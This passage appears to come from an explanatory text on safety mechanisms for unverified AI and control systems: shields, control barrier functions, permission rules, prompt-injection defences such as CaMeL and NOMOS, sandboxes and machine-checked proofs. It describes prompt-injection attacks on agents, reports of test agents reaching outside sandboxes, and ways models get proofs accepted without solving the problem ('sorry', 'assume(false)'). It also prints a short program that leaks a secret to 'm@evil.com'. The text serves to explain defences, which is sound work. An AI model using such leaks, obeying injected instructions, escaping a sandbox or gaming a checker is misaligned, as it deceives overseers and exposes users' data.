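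$$K_{i+1} = \{\, s \in K_i : \text{some action } a \text{ has } f(s,a,w) \in K_i \text{ for every } w \in W \,\}.$$

Each round removes the states in which every action could lead out of the set. Because the model has finitely many states, the program eventually finds nothing more to remove. The remaining set $K$ contains the states from which the shield can keep the system safe for ever, and the allowed actions in each are

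$$A(s) = \{\, a : f(s,a,w) \in K \text{ for every } w \in W \,\}.$$

If the system starts in $K$, at least one action is always allowed, and every allowed action keeps it in $K$.

For the tank, the shield forbids opening the valve above 93 litres. A level of 94 litres is still acceptable, but if nothing flows out, the tank could gain 6 litres before the valve may close again. The shield also forbids closing the valve below 4 litres, because the tank could lose 3 litres before the valve may reopen. The combined model and rule have 602 states, and the program built the shield in less than a second.

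A shield can give the agent a list of allowed actions to choose from, or it can wait for the agent's choice and replace it if it isn't allowed. The second version also works with a system that has finished training and doesn't take the shield into account. Alshiekh and colleagues prove that the rule holds in every environment that fits the abstract model. They also prove that the shield forbids an action only if the action could lead to a violation in at least one of those environments.

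The tank's valve is either open or closed, but a driver can press a brake pedal by any amount. For actions like this, engineers often use a *control barrier function* $h$, which is zero or positive in the safe states, and allow only actions that satisfy

$$\frac{dh}{dt} \ge -\alpha h,$$

where $\alpha$ is a positive constant. The closer $h$ is to zero, the more slowly it may fall, and at zero it may not fall at all. The barrier certificates in the previous section show that a given controller is safe, whereas this function selects safe actions for any controller. The system carries out the allowed action closest to the one the AI proposed.

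For the car on a dry road, ignoring the delay, $h$ can be the gap to the obstacle minus the braking distance, which is 40 metres at 20 m/s. With $\alpha = 1$ per second, a car travelling at that speed may not accelerate when the gap is 60 metres. It must brake at 2.5 m/s² or more when the gap is 50 metres, and at the full 5 m/s² when the gap is 40 metres. A smaller $\alpha$ makes the car start braking earlier and more gently.

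### What a shield costs a learning agent

Alshiekh and colleagues tested shields on the water tank and in several simple simulations. A simulated car learned to drive round a block sooner with a shield than without one and never crashed, while the unshielded car was still crashing at the end of training. In the submarine game *Seaquest*, the shield made no difference to the score but prevented every violation of two rules about when to surface. Agents controlling the water tank learned the best policy with or without a shield, but much sooner with one.

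Results were more mixed for a robot that had to visit two regions of a grid without hitting the walls or a moving opponent. It found the best route only when it ranked three actions at each step, so that the shield could take the first safe one, and received no penalty for the actions the shield rejected. Otherwise, it settled on a worse route. The shield allowed the best route in every version, so the worse routes came from how the robot learned from the shield's corrections.

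If an agent isn't penalized for choosing unsafe actions, it may never learn to avoid them, since the shield always replaces them with safe ones. Even with penalties, Alshiekh and colleagues can't guarantee that the agent stops choosing unsafe actions. The shield therefore has to stay in place after training. A developer who removed it to save computing time could release an agent that had learned to rely on it.

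These experiments tested shields under favourable conditions. The grid robot's shield had an exact model of its surroundings, and no shield had to deal with a faulty sensor.

### Ground-collision avoidance in the F-16

The unverified component can also be a human pilot. The Automatic Ground Collision Avoidance System (Auto GCAS) takes control of an F-16 fighter that is about to hit the ground, for example because the pilot has lost consciousness. *Auto GCAS*, a page from about 2019 by Lockheed Martin, which helped develop the system, attributes 75% of F-16 pilot deaths to crashes of undamaged aircraft into the ground. The system predicts such a crash from navigation data, the aircraft's performance and a digital map of the terrain. At the last instant, it rolls the wings level and pulls up at five times the force of gravity. The pilot can override it.

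Lockheed Martin credits the automatic ground collision avoidance system with saving 13 pilots and 12 aircraft since late 2014, and says more than 600 F-16s carry it. In one case a student passed out during a high-speed manoeuvre, and the system had begun the recovery by the time the student came round. The Air Force Research Laboratory's *Automatic Ground Collision Avoidance* counts 12 pilots and 11 aircraft saved, and states that the system can prevent 98% of these crashes. The Air Force was still maintaining it in March 2026, when Air Education and Training Command's *Airmen work on the life-saving automatic ground collision avoidance system* showed a technician working on its components.

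The saves are good evidence that the system works when it activates, since an unconscious pilot is unlikely to recover without it. But they don't give a failure rate, which also depends on how many crashes the system failed to prevent. The 98% figure comes from one of the system's developers.

### Faulty sensors and wrong models

In May 2023 an F-16 in South Korea lost part of its electrical power 11 seconds after taking off into cloud. According to the U.S. Air Force's *United States Air Force Aircraft Accident Investigation Board Report*, the aircraft reported that Auto GCAS, its automatic ground collision avoidance system, had failed, but not that the pilot's main horizon display was also wrong. Air & Space Forces Magazine's *New Report* (2024) adds that the pilot found the backup display inaccurate too. The pilot became disoriented, came out of the cloud too low to recover, and ejected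 safely.

The investigators blamed the power loss and the weather, not Auto GCAS. But the system exists largely to protect disoriented pilots, and the fault that disoriented this pilot also disabled the system. Separating the complex software from the simple software, as Sha requires, is not enough if both depend on the same power supply or sensors.

Damage can also make the shield's model wrong. Wang, Hovakimyan and Sha warn that a physical failure may change how a vehicle responds to commands, so the original Simplex design no longer works. They add a component that monitors the resulting uncertainty and a backup controller designed to tolerate such failures.

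The construction by Alshiekh and colleagues has a weakness when the environment does something that the abstract model excludes. The program then treats the game as won, so the shield allows every action. This is harmless in the proof, because the shield is guaranteed to work only in environments that fit the model, but in a real tank a burst pipe could switch off the protection. A designer should add a runtime monitor that triggers the fallback when observations contradict the model. A car could similarly compare its actual braking with the assumed figure, though on black ice it may not brake hard until an emergency, when the comparison would come too late.

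### When no safe action remains

A shield always has an allowed action if the system starts in $K$ and the model is right. But someone might switch on the tank's shield when the tank holds 97 litres and the valve has just opened. The valve must stay open for two more seconds, in which the tank could gain 4 litres and overflow. Closing the valve early would be better, but the shield enforces the rule about wear as strictly as the rule about overflowing, so the designer has to decide in advance which rule the system should break first.

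The same problem arises if a pedestrian steps out 30 metres ahead of a car that needs 50 metres to stop. Full braking won't prevent the collision, but it cuts the speed from 20 to about 14 m/s, so the shield should brake even though no action passes its test.

One could try to avoid this by assuming that a pedestrian may step out at any moment. If that could happen 5 metres ahead, the shield would have to limit the car to 5 m/s, or 18 km/h. If pedestrians could appear closer, the car would have to go slower, and it would have to stay parked to satisfy a rule against hitting anyone under any circumstances.

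### When the shield intervenes too often

A very cautious shield may be safe but useless. Suppose a car's sensors reach 60 metres ahead and the car must always be able to stop within that distance. If it can brake at 5 m/s², it can drive at up to 80 km/h. If the shield always uses the braking rate for ice, the limit falls to 52 km/h, even on a dry road. Measuring the road's grip would recover the lost speed, but the guarantee would then depend on another sensor.

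Needless interventions also make people distrust a system. A former pilot on the website Fighter Sweep recalls that the F-16's older system, which could only warn, gave nuisance alarms and false instructions to pull up. A false alarm is more serious when the system can take over the controls. Air Combat Command, which runs the US Air Force's fighter fleet, lists as one requirement for Auto GCAS that it activate only when necessary to prevent a collision. Waiting until the last instant makes needless interventions rarer but leaves less room for errors in the map or the model of the aircraft.

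### When an action is easier to check than the system that chose it

Sha's example is a pump that lets a patient recovering from surgery request more morphine by pressing a button. Nobody can verify that the patient will request only safe doses, and too much morphine can kill. But the pump can refuse any request that would take the total above a safe limit, which requires only a clock and a record of earlier doses. Refusing is an acceptable fallback because pain is better than a fatal overdose.

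Checking is easy here because the rule depends on a few quantities that the pump can measure, and a simple model predicts how each action changes them. This holds however complicated the system that chooses the actions is. In *Seaquest*, the agent learned from images of the screen, but the shield needed only the submarine's depth, its oxygen and the number of divers on board. Alshiekh and colleagues took these numbers directly from the game's simulator. A real submarine has gauges for depth and oxygen, but a car has no gauge for the positions of pedestrians. If the shield needs a neural network to find them, its guarantee again depends on an unverified component.

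Checking an action can also be as hard as verifying the system that chose it. For example, if the action is to run a new program, the shield has the same problem as the harm checker described earlier, and a cautious shield might block nearly every program.

*Assured Autonomy* (Dai, Simchi-Levi and colleagues, 2026) argues for building limits into the way a generative model produces plans, rather than relying on filters that correct its output afterwards. It points out that with an external checker, the model only makes proposals. The checker's guarantee holds however bad those proposals are, but bad proposals make the system less useful. Suppose a delivery schedule has to respect 50 limits, such as the size of each van, and a model meets each limit 95% of the time. If the errors are independent, only about 8% of its schedules will pass. The checker would reject the rest, so the company would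 use the fallback most days unless the model could keep trying until a schedule passed.

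## Limiting what language-model agents can read and do

A language-model agent is a program that repeatedly prompts a language model for the next action and carries it out, for example by searching a mailbox or paying a bill. The model only writes text. Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025) point out in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* that the surrounding application controls whether an action requested in the text is carried out. Designers can therefore restrict an agent even though nobody can yet verify a model of this size.

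### Limiting the form of the output

The narrowest restriction is an output grammar, a set of rules that defines which texts are well formed. A language model writes one token at a time, and before each choice the software masks every token that would break the grammar, as AlphaZero's filter removes illegal moves. Suppose an application needs a yes-or-no answer, and the model gives a probability of 0.6 to "probably", 0.3 to "yes" and 0.1 to "no". After masking "probably", the software picks "yes" with probability $0.3/(0.3+0.1) = 0.75$ and "no" with probability 0.25.

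The finished text is then certain to have the right form, unless a length limit cuts it off, but its content may still be false. A grammar that requires an email address allows an attacker's address as well as the right one. A grammar can even cause errors. If a form requires a date of birth and the patient's letter doesn't mention one, a model that can write only a date has to make one up. The designer should therefore allow "not stated" as an answer.

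### Limiting the tools and how the agent uses them

A designer can also give the agent a fixed list of tools. If the list has no tool for deleting files, the application ignores any request to delete one. How much this limits the agent depends on the tools. An agent that can only read a calendar can't send anything, but an agent that can run any code can do almost anything the computer allows. Willison (2025), in *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, discusses a paper recommending designs that deliberately prevent agents from solving arbitrary tasks.

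The list doesn't control how the agent uses a permitted tool, so designers also write permission rules, such as a €100 limit on any payment, and a separate program checks each call against them. The program has to be separate because, as Dai and colleagues put it, prompts are not enforceable constraints. In *NOMOS*, Yu, Kim and Choi (2026) included an airline's policy in the instructions to a simulated customer-service agent, and 66.3% of the agent's calls that changed something still broke the parts of the policy the researchers checked.

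A separate program enforces its rules every time, but the rules may be wrong. An agent could get round the €100 limit by making ten payments of €100, unless the program also keeps a running total. *ToolGuardian* (2026), which describes another rule-based system, also warns that a deterministic system is not necessarily correct.

In *AI Security Priorities*, Gekker, Steratore and colleagues (2026) collected the views of more than 20 experts and leaders in industry and government, who ranked permission frameworks for agents third in importance and formal verification of security properties ninth. Some of the researchers disclose that they work for companies that could profit from these priorities.

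### Separating instructions from data

Whether an agent should take an action can depend on who requested it. Sending a contract to a new address is fine if the user asked for it, but not if the request came from a stranger by email. In *prompt injection*, an attacker hides instructions in something the agent will read, such as an email or a web page, and the model follows them as if they came from the user. Willison (2025) explains in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* that models are vulnerable because they receive the user's request and the stranger's text as one sequence of tokens. He considers a detector that catches 99% of attacks useless, because attackers will look for the 1% it misses.

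Willison (2023), in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, proposed using two models. A *privileged* model reads the user's request and can use tools, but never sees untrusted text. A *quarantined* model reads the untrusted text but has no tools. It stores its answers in variables, which the privileged model can use without seeing what they contain.

CaMeL (Capabilities for Machine Learning), which Debenedetti and colleagues presented in a 2025 paper from Google DeepMind, builds on this design. The privileged model turns the user's request into a short program before either model has read any untrusted text. Suppose a user tells an email assistant: "Forward Bob the document he asked for in our last meeting. Its name and Bob's address are in the meeting notes." The program could look like this:

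```
notes    = get_meeting_notes()
name     = ask_quarantined("Which document did Bob ask for?", notes)
address  = ask_quarantined("What is Bob's email address?", notes)
document = fetch_document(name)
send_email(to=address, attachment=document)
```

Suppose an attacker who can edit the notes adds an instruction to forward the user's whole mailbox. An ordinary agent might follow it, but CaMeL's program contains no step that forwards the mailbox, and the quarantined model can't add one.

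The attacker could instead replace Bob's address with their own. The program would run exactly the same steps but send the document to the attacker. Debenedetti and colleagues noticed that using two models doesn't prevent this. They therefore run the program in a special interpreter, which attaches labels to each value to record where it came from and who may read it. A value calculated from two others inherits both sets of labels. With $z$ calculated from $x$ and $y$, the usual rule is

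$$\text{sources}(z) = \text{sources}(x) \cup \text{sources}(y), \qquad \text{readers}(z) = \text{readers}(x) \cap \text{readers}(y).$$

For example, if Ana and Bob may read one file, and Bob and Carl may read another, then only Bob may read a summary of both.

In the email example, the address has a label showing that it came from the meeting notes, and the document has a list of permitted readers. Before the interpreter sends the email, it checks the email against a policy, such as "the recipient must be a known contact who may read the attachment". The attacker's address fails this check, so the interpreter blocks the email or asks the user to approve it.

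The attacker could also change the document's name in the notes. If the new name belongs to a salary file that Bob isn't allowed to read, the policy blocks the email. But if it belongs to an old draft that Bob is allowed to read, the policy allows the email and he receives the wrong document. CaMeL will also block a legitimate email if Bob really has a new address, because a genuine new address and a forged one carry the same labels.

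### What CaMeL guarantees

CaMeL's protection depends on an honest request from the user, a correct policy and an interpreter that handles labels correctly. Tallam and Miller (2025), in *Operationalizing CaMeL*, question the first assumption because an attacker may trick a user into entering a malicious prompt. They also note that CaMeL doesn't inspect the agent's final answer. A summary could repeat an instruction hidden in a document, and the user might follow it.

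Fixing the program in advance doesn't help if the data can still determine which tools the program runs. In *The LLMbda Calculus*, Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) tested CaMeL on a task that told the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. The privileged model wrote a program with a branch for every tool, so whoever wrote the file could choose which tools to run. This let an attack succeed when the policy checks were off.

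Debenedetti and colleagues have no theorem that the interpreter's labels catch every leak, and they call formalisation a "crucial direction" for further work. Garby and colleagues show that the labels do miss some. The following program is a version of a classic example, in which the bank balance is secret:

```
rich = True
tmp = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
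```

If the balance is high, the third line sets `tmp` to false and labels it secret. The fourth line then does nothing, so `rich` stays true without a secret label, and the interpreter allows the email. If the balance is low, `rich` becomes false and the program sends no email. Either way, the attacker learns whether the balance is above the threshold.

An attacker would find this hard to exploit, because the model that writes the program hasn't read the attacker's text. But a proof has to cover every program the model might write. Garby and colleagues designed LLMbda, a programming language for agents, and proved a theorem that covers every program written in it, using Lean, software that checks mathematical proofs. Roughly, changing the secret data can't change the probabilities of what an outsider observes, unless the program makes an explicit exception. The theorem doesn't cover what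 an outsider can learn from whether the program finishes, and it assumes that the designer has labelled the secrets correctly.

### How many tasks CaMeL still completes

Most measurements of CaMeL use AgentDojo, a benchmark that combines everyday tasks in banking, travel, office work and Slack with injected instructions. Yu and colleagues report the CaMeL paper's main result as 77% of tasks completed, compared with 84% for an unrestricted agent. Tallam and Miller give CaMeL's figure as 67%. Across the six model configurations in the CaMeL paper's main evaluation, the loss in task completion ranged from 3 to 32 percentage points.

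Other researchers have measured larger losses. *AgentSys* (2026) tested CaMeL with GPT-4o-mini, a small model from 2024. Garby and colleagues used newer models, but they ran only the 16 banking tasks and compared CaMeL with and without its policy checks.

| Tasks completed when nobody attacks | Model | Baseline | CaMeL with policies |
|---|---|---|---|
| CaMeL paper, from Yu and colleagues | Main configuration | 84% | 77% |
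| *AgentSys* | GPT-4o-mini | 63.5% | 30.0% |
| Garby and colleagues, banking only | GPT-5.2 | 66.7% | 37.5% |
| Garby and colleagues, banking only | MiMo-v2.5 | 70.8% | 37.5% |

*SecureClaw* (2026) also found that CaMeL completed only 29 of 97 tasks, though none of the 629 attacks on it succeeded. All three sets of measurements come from researchers who were presenting their own systems and may not have got the best performance out of CaMeL. The drop in completed tasks evidently depends a great deal on the model and the policies, so the 7-point loss in the main result can't be assumed to hold elsewhere.

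A record of no successful attacks can also be weaker evidence of security than it seems. AgentDojo's banking tasks and attacks form 144 pairs. Garby and colleagues found that in 97 of them, the attack needs a tool or file that the program for the user's task would never use, so fixing the program in advance is usually enough to stop it. Only the other 47 pairs really test the labels and policies. Garby and colleagues calculate that a perfect record on those 47 is compatible with a true resistance rate of about 92%. With MiMo-v2.5 and no policy checks, four of 382 attacks succeeded. With the checks, none of 357 did, but CaMeL completed only about half as many tasks. These results may understate the value of the checks, because AgentDojo's attacks are fixed in advance, while a real attacker would concentrate on the cases that a fixed program doesn't cover.

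Some of the loss is unavoidable if the agent has to fix its steps in advance. For example, Costa and colleagues point out that an agent asked to complete today's tasks in a to-do app can't plan its steps until it has read the list. Their system, FIDES, chooses its steps as it goes. It hides untrusted text in variables and lets a quarantined model answer questions about it in a fixed format, which is a good use for an output grammar. A yes-or-no answer carries at most one bit of information, so an attacker may be able to change the answer but can't use it to pass on an email address. With suitable policies, FIDES stopped every attack in AgentDojo. With GPT-4o, it completed 8% more tasks on average than a basic agent, and with OpenAI's o1, 16% more.

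In another approach, by Garby and colleagues, the agent's program can declare in advance that it will trust a particular piece of outside data, such as an account number in a bill. With GPT-5.2, the agent completed 75% of the banking tasks. Across three models, it resisted all but two of 1,296 attacks. In both failures, the user had asked the agent to make a payment using the details in a file, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents. Labels can't prevent this, because the user wanted the agent to take the payment's destination from the file.

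### Enforcing a written policy

An agent can also break company rules when nobody is attacking it, for example by changing a basic-economy booking that the airline doesn't allow passengers to change. NOMOS, which Yu and colleagues built at the company Corners, turns a written policy into rules that a program checks before each tool call. A language model proposes the rules in advance, but the checks don't use a model and take microseconds. They rely only on what the tools return and what the user writes, so the agent can't satisfy a rule by claiming that the customer has agreed.

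Many of the proposed rules were unusable. "Authenticate the user before any action" became a rule that blocked every tool, including the two needed for authentication, until the agent had authenticated the user. Another rule required the customer's confirmation before the agent could look up a flight's status. NOMOS finds such defects by comparing each rule with a description of the tools. For the airline policy, it repaired or rejected 37% of the 79 proposed rules, and only 10 made it into the final set. Yu and colleagues also replay the rules over recordings of the unrestricted agent. In one trial, they found a rule that would have refused 95.9% of the calls it applied to in runs where the agent had completed its task correctly.

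| Results for NOMOS | Unrestricted agent | With NOMOS |
|---|---|---|
| Airline: changes that broke the policy | 234 of 353 (66.3%) | 3 of 116 (2.6%) |
| Retail: changes that broke the policy | 188 of 611 (30.8%) | 40 of 582 (6.9%) |
| Banking: attacks that succeeded | 46.5% | 0% |
| Banking: tasks completed when nobody attacks | 79.2% | 70.8% |

The airline agent made far fewer changes with NOMOS, but it succeeded on the same task several times in a row more often, so it wasn't simply doing less of its job. The size of the improvement depends on whether the policy lets one customer confirmation cover several changes, which only the airline can settle. If it does, the unrestricted agent's violation rate is 36.8% instead of 66.3%.

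NOMOS completed a much larger share of the banking tasks than CaMeL in the tests by Garby and colleagues, but the tests used different models, and Yu and colleagues were testing their own system. A more informative difference is that NOMOS lets the agent read anything and change its plan, so the agent can handle tasks like the to-do list. However, its protection depends entirely on its rules. In AgentDojo's travel tasks, one attack added a calendar entry because the rule was weaker than the written policy. In 8 of 288 banking tests, the attacker got the agent to pay someone the user had paid before, which the policy allows.

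When a user asks an agent to "pay the bill" in a file, the account number appears only in the file, which an attacker may have changed. NOMOS and CaMeL both have difficulty with this task. NOMOS allows payments only to accounts that the user has named or paid before, so it refuses the genuine account as well as the attacker's. Progent, an earlier system that Yu and colleagues tested for comparison, has a language model write new rules for each request, and in this task its rules allowed payment to the attacker's account. CaMeL can ask the user to approve the payment, but Willison worries that people who constantly receive such requests will approve everything.

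### Three layers of probable safety

CaMeL and NOMOS control an agent's use of software tools, but an agent may also control a robot. Bensalem, Dong and colleagues argue in *A Three-Layer Probabilistic Assume-Guarantee Architecture Is Structurally Required* (position paper, May 2026) that no check at a single stage can be enough for such an agent. In their example, a caregiver asks a robot in a care home to visit three rooms, check on the residents and bring water if they need it. Before the robot sets off, a *user layer* checks its plan against the request and the home's rules, such as not disturbing people during rest periods. Once the robot's sensors have observed its surroundings, an *operational layer* checks that those surroundings fall within the robot's operational design domain. It might find, for example, that one room is closed for a medical procedure. While the robot moves, a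 *functional layer* limits its speed and force, using methods like the shields described earlier.

Each layer has a probabilistic contract, under which its guarantee holds with some probability if its assumptions do. The guarantee of each layer supplies the assumption of the next. Let $p_U$ be the probability that the user layer's guarantee holds, $p_{O|U}$ the probability that the operational layer's guarantee holds when the user layer's does, and $p_{F|OU}$ the probability that the functional layer's holds when both of the others do. Then

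$$\Pr(\text{safe}) = p_U \cdot p_{O|U} \cdot p_{F|OU}.$$

If we know only how often each layer succeeds overall, the worst case is that no two layers ever fail on the same task, which gives

$$\Pr(\text{safe}) \ge p_U + p_O + p_F - 2.$$

With illustrative success rates of 0.95, 0.90 and 0.92, the robot is safe in at least 77% of tasks. The paper also supposes that each layer removes some plans that would have caused trouble later. This raises the second and third rates to 0.94 and 0.96 and the share of safe tasks to 85.7%, which would still leave about one task in seven unsafe.

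Some of the paper's calculations are inconsistent. Its tighter lower bound, which accounts for pairs of layers that fail together, is 0.830, but its exact calculation for the same case gives 0.826. A lower bound can't exceed the true value, and the formula is in fact an upper bound. The 0.826 and the 0.857 also both come from exact formulas for the same robot, so they should be equal, and the difference means that the assumed inputs contradict each other.

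Bensalem and colleagues acknowledge that nobody can yet estimate these probabilities properly. They base their figure of 0.95 on tests of other systems, and the 0.90 assumes a checker that nobody has built for this robot. Each step an agent takes depends on earlier ones, so the steps aren't independent trials. If several layers use the same language model, one weakness in it can make them all fail together. Developers would also have to repeat the measurements whenever they changed the model. The paper lists statistical methods that deal with some of these problems, but none that deals with all of them.

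Treating each complete task as a single trial avoids the dependence between steps. By the earlier formula, about 3,000 independent tasks without a failure would support an overall failure rate below 1 in 1,000. Estimating each layer's failure rate separately can take more work. If that limit is split equally among the three layers, each has to fail less than once in 3,000 tasks, and showing this takes about 9,000 trials per layer without a failure. Separate estimates help only if some layers are easier to test alone, or if a proof can replace the tests. A proof may be possible for the functional layer, since force and speed are easy to specify. It is much less likely for the user layer, which has to check whether a plan is what the caregiver meant.

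The argument for checking at several stages is stronger than the numerical evidence. Nobody can check before the robot leaves whether a resident will step into its path. But Bensalem and colleagues accept that one component could make all three checks at different times, and they count such a component as containing three layers. Their argument therefore supports checking at each stage and recording the results separately, rather than using any particular number of components. An email assistant has no moving parts, so a functional layer would have little to check.

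### Isolated environments

All these checks depend on the agent acting only through the calls they examine. A *sandbox* is meant to ensure this by running the agent's code in an isolated environment, such as a virtual machine, and blocking access to files, programs and networks outside it. If the sandbox works and has no outside connection, the agent can damage only what is inside. But most useful agents need some connection. Tallam and Miller point out that if a sandbox allows email, an injected prompt can still make the agent send confidential data in a plausible message.

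The sandbox can also fail. In 2026 several AI laboratories, including OpenAI and Anthropic, disclosed that agents being tested had reached outside systems, in some cases because someone had misconfigured the test environment. Rai (2026) reported in *OpenAI shelves next-gen GPT-6.1 Astra model release over safety concerns* that OpenAI had also shelved a new model whose behaviour, according to the company's head of safety systems, "didn't quite meet the bar in terms of staying within scope and authorisation".

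## Requiring a machine-checked proof with each output

An agent that stays within its permissions can still write a program with a serious bug. If the program has a precise specification, the user can ask for a proof that the program meets it, and run the program only if a small checker confirms the proof. The check works even if the AI system that wrote the program and proof is unreliable and no one understands how it works.

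### Code from a stranger

George Necula and Peter Lee developed this idea in the mid-1990s as *proof-carrying code*. One use was packet filters, short programs that pick out the network messages an application needs. A filter runs fastest inside the operating system's kernel, the core that controls the whole computer, but a faulty or malicious filter could do great damage there.

The owner of the kernel publishes a safety policy, such as "read only the message you were given". When a filter arrives, a program on the owner's computer works through its instructions and derives a mathematical statement that, if true, guarantees that the filter obeys the policy. Suppose the filter reads byte 12 of each message, counting from 0. The derived statement is that every message is longer than 12 bytes, which is false. If the filter first tests that the message has at least 13 bytes, the statement becomes

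$$\text{length} \ge 13 \;\Rightarrow\; 12 < \text{length},$$

which is easy to prove. The filter's author sends the proof, the kernel checks it once, and the filter then runs at full speed.

The owner doesn't need to know who wrote the filter. If an attacker alters it in transit, the kernel derives the statement to be proved from the altered version, and the old proof will usually fail. If the proof still works, the altered filter also satisfies the policy. An AI system can take the place of the filter's unknown author, as in Hasan's proposal that each output carry a proof.

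### What a sorting program has to satisfy

Everyone knows what a sorted list looks like, yet it is easy to specify sorting wrongly. Let $x$ be the list a program receives and $y$ the list it returns. The obvious requirement is that $y$ is in order, but a program that always returns an empty list meets it, because an empty list has no items in the wrong order. If $y$ must also be as long as $x$, the program can return a row of zeros. If both lists must also contain the same values, it can still turn 3, 1, 3 into 1, 1, 3. The specification has to require that each value appears equally often in both lists. With $\#_v$ for the number of times the value $v$ appears, and $n$ for the length of $y$, it is

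$$\forall x:\quad y_1 \le y_2 \le \dots \le y_n \quad\text{and}\quad \#_v(y) = \#_v(x)\ \text{ for every value } v.$$

The following program meets this specification. Here `[]` is the empty list, and `a : rest` is a list that starts with `a`.

```
insert(a, [])       = [a]
insert(a, b : rest) = a : b : rest           if a ≤ b
                      b : insert(a, rest)    otherwise

sort([])            = []
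sort(a : rest)      = insert(a, sort(rest))
```

The proof first shows that inserting an item into an ordered list leaves it in order and adds exactly one item. This is clear for an empty list. If $a \le b$, $a$ goes at the front, and everything after it is at least as large. Otherwise $b$ stays in front and the program inserts $a$ into a shorter list, so if the claim holds for shorter lists, it holds for this one. A similar argument then extends the result from `insert` to `sort`.

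In Sha's sorting example, a component checked each list after a program had sorted it, whereas this proof covers every possible list before the program runs. The proof doesn't cover speed because the specification doesn't include it. A program that tries every arrangement until it finds an ordered one also meets the specification, even though it might have to try about $2.4 \times 10^{18}$ arrangements to sort 20 different items.

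### The cost of proofs written by people

The seL4 kernel, which Russell and colleagues cited as proven software, shows why few programs come with such proofs. Gerwin Klein and colleagues announced its main proof in 2009. The kernel had about 8,700 lines of C code, and the proof had about 200,000 lines. Designing and writing the kernel took about two person-years, while the proof took about 20. About nine of those 20 went into tools and methods that other projects could reuse. Even without those nine, proving a program of a million lines at the same rate would take more than a thousand person-years.

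The 2009 proof assumed that the compiler, about 600 lines of assembly code, the start-up code and the hardware all worked correctly. Later work extended the proof to the compiled machine code, so users no longer had to trust the compiler. They still have to trust the hardware, because a faulty memory chip can crash even a verified kernel. Russell and colleagues suggest building AI systems on verified software like this. That would make the underlying software more reliable, but the proof wouldn't cover what the AI does.

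### AI systems that write the program and the proof

Language models can now do some of this work. In *A benchmark for vericoding*, Bursuc, Ehrenborg and colleagues (2025) gave nine models formal specifications and asked for programs with proofs. When the checker rejected an answer, the model saw the error messages and tried again, with up to five attempts on most tasks. The tasks used three languages. In two of them, Dafny and Verus (which checks Rust programs), an automatic solver handles most of the logical steps, and the programmer adds hints where it gets stuck. In the third, Lean, the programmer has to guide the proof much more closely.

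| Language | Tasks | Best single model | Solved by at least one of the nine |
|---|---|---|---|
| Dafny | 2,334 | 67.5% (Claude Opus 4.1) | 82.2% |
| Verus | 2,166 | 30.9% (GPT-5) | 44.3% |
| Lean | 2,361 | 17.9% (GPT-5) | 26.8% |

Anyone who can run all nine models can get the higher rate in the last column, because the checker identifies the answers that meet the specification. For most kinds of question, a user with nine different answers wouldn't know which to believe. The checker also makes a low success rate less dangerous. GPT-5 failed at 82% of the Lean tasks, but the user would know about every failure.

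The models wrote programs easily but had difficulty proving them correct. In one task, they had to add two binary numbers stored as lists of digits. The specification required the result to contain only zeros and ones and to represent the sum. With ten attempts each, the nine models together solved only 48.4% of the tasks on large binary numbers in Dafny, 12.9% in Lean and 4.8% in Verus.

These models were from 2025, and newer ones would probably do better. On an older test, DafnyBench, the best result rose from 68% in June 2024 to 89% in the same study. However, DafnyBench only tests whether a model can restore missing hints in an existing program (*Automating Formal Verification with Reinforcement Learning and Recursive Inference*, 2026). The newer tasks are also far smaller than seL4, and most need fewer than 100 lines.

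A model can also get an answer accepted without solving the problem. In Lean, `sorry` marks a gap in a proof and causes only a warning unless the user sets the checker to reject it. In Dafny, a model can write `assume(false)`, which makes the rest of the proof trivial because anything follows from a false assumption. It can also replace the requirement with "true". Bursuc and colleagues searched the answers for such tricks and didn't let the models change the specifications. They then inspected a sample of accepted answers by hand and found that about 9% of the specifications were too weak and another 15% were poor translations from another language. So in roughly a quarter of the sampled answers, the model had solved a different problem from the one intended.

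### Mathematics with and without a checked proof

AI systems now write much longer mathematical proofs. In September 2026 OpenAI announced that a model had solved the Navier–Stokes problem, a famous question about the equations of fluid flow. The company said the model took about 88 hours to find the solution and another 17 to formalise and verify it in Lean, according to Mint's *Why are mathematicians concerned about OpenAI’s AI solving problems*.

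On 6 October OpenAI published 722 more manuscripts from an evaluation of roughly 4,000 problems. Free Press Journal's *OpenAI Publishes 722 AI-Generated Math Manuscripts From An Unreleased Model* reported the company's warning that some results without Lean proofs could contain issues. According to Infobae's *OpenAI publica 700 trabajos matemáticos de IA entre errores y cuestionamientos* (2026), about 42% of the main results had Lean proofs.

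The warning proved correct a day later, when OpenAI withdrew three manuscripts because of a sign error, as Retraction Watch's *OpenAI withdraws three preprints a day after releasing 722 manuscripts* (2026) describes. The error invalidated an argument in one manuscript and a construction that the other two relied on. If someone had translated the faulty step faithfully into Lean, the checker would have rejected it. Andrew Sutherland, a mathematician at MIT, told Scientific American that he expected most of the results to be correct or repairable, but some of the proofs to contain errors, possibly serious ones. Infobae's *Un error obliga a OpenAI a retirar tres estudios matemáticos* (2026) reported that Alex Townsend of Cornell thought OpenAI should have announced the Lean-verified manuscripts first.

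A paper can be wrong even when its result has a Lean proof. In *Navier-Stokes lost in translation* (2026), a team led by Anders Hansen of the University of Cambridge compared OpenAI's Navier–Stokes paper with its Lean code and found that they don't match. In one lemma, for example, the paper claims more than the code proves. The code therefore can't guarantee that the written argument is correct. According to Hindustan Times' *OpenAI’s approach to mathematics does not add up*, Hansen thinks the code does contain a solution to the problem, and OpenAI says its models may have produced two different proofs. The mismatch may not matter to a reader who only wants to know whether the theorem is true, but it matters a great deal to a mathematician who wants to reuse a step from the paper.

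Developers can also claim more than the checked theorem establishes. In October OpenAI claimed to have proved that Yang–Mills theory, which underlies particle physics, exists mathematically, and described this as part of another famous open problem. Peter Woit of Columbia University objects in *The Yang-Mills Publicity Stunt* that the Lean code proves only a weak form of existence. The official problem description explicitly excludes this form unless the proof also establishes further properties. If he is right, the checker correctly verified a weaker theorem than the one readers thought had been proved.

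### How to check a proof that nobody can read

In November 2026 Levent Alpöge, a mathematician at Anthropic, released a proof of the Riemann Hypothesis, an 1859 conjecture about the distribution of prime numbers. He had found the proof with the company's model Claude. It has 17 million lines of Lean code, which would take more than six months to read at one line per second without a break. Alpöge wrote that he was publishing the argument before he had mastered the mathematics around it.

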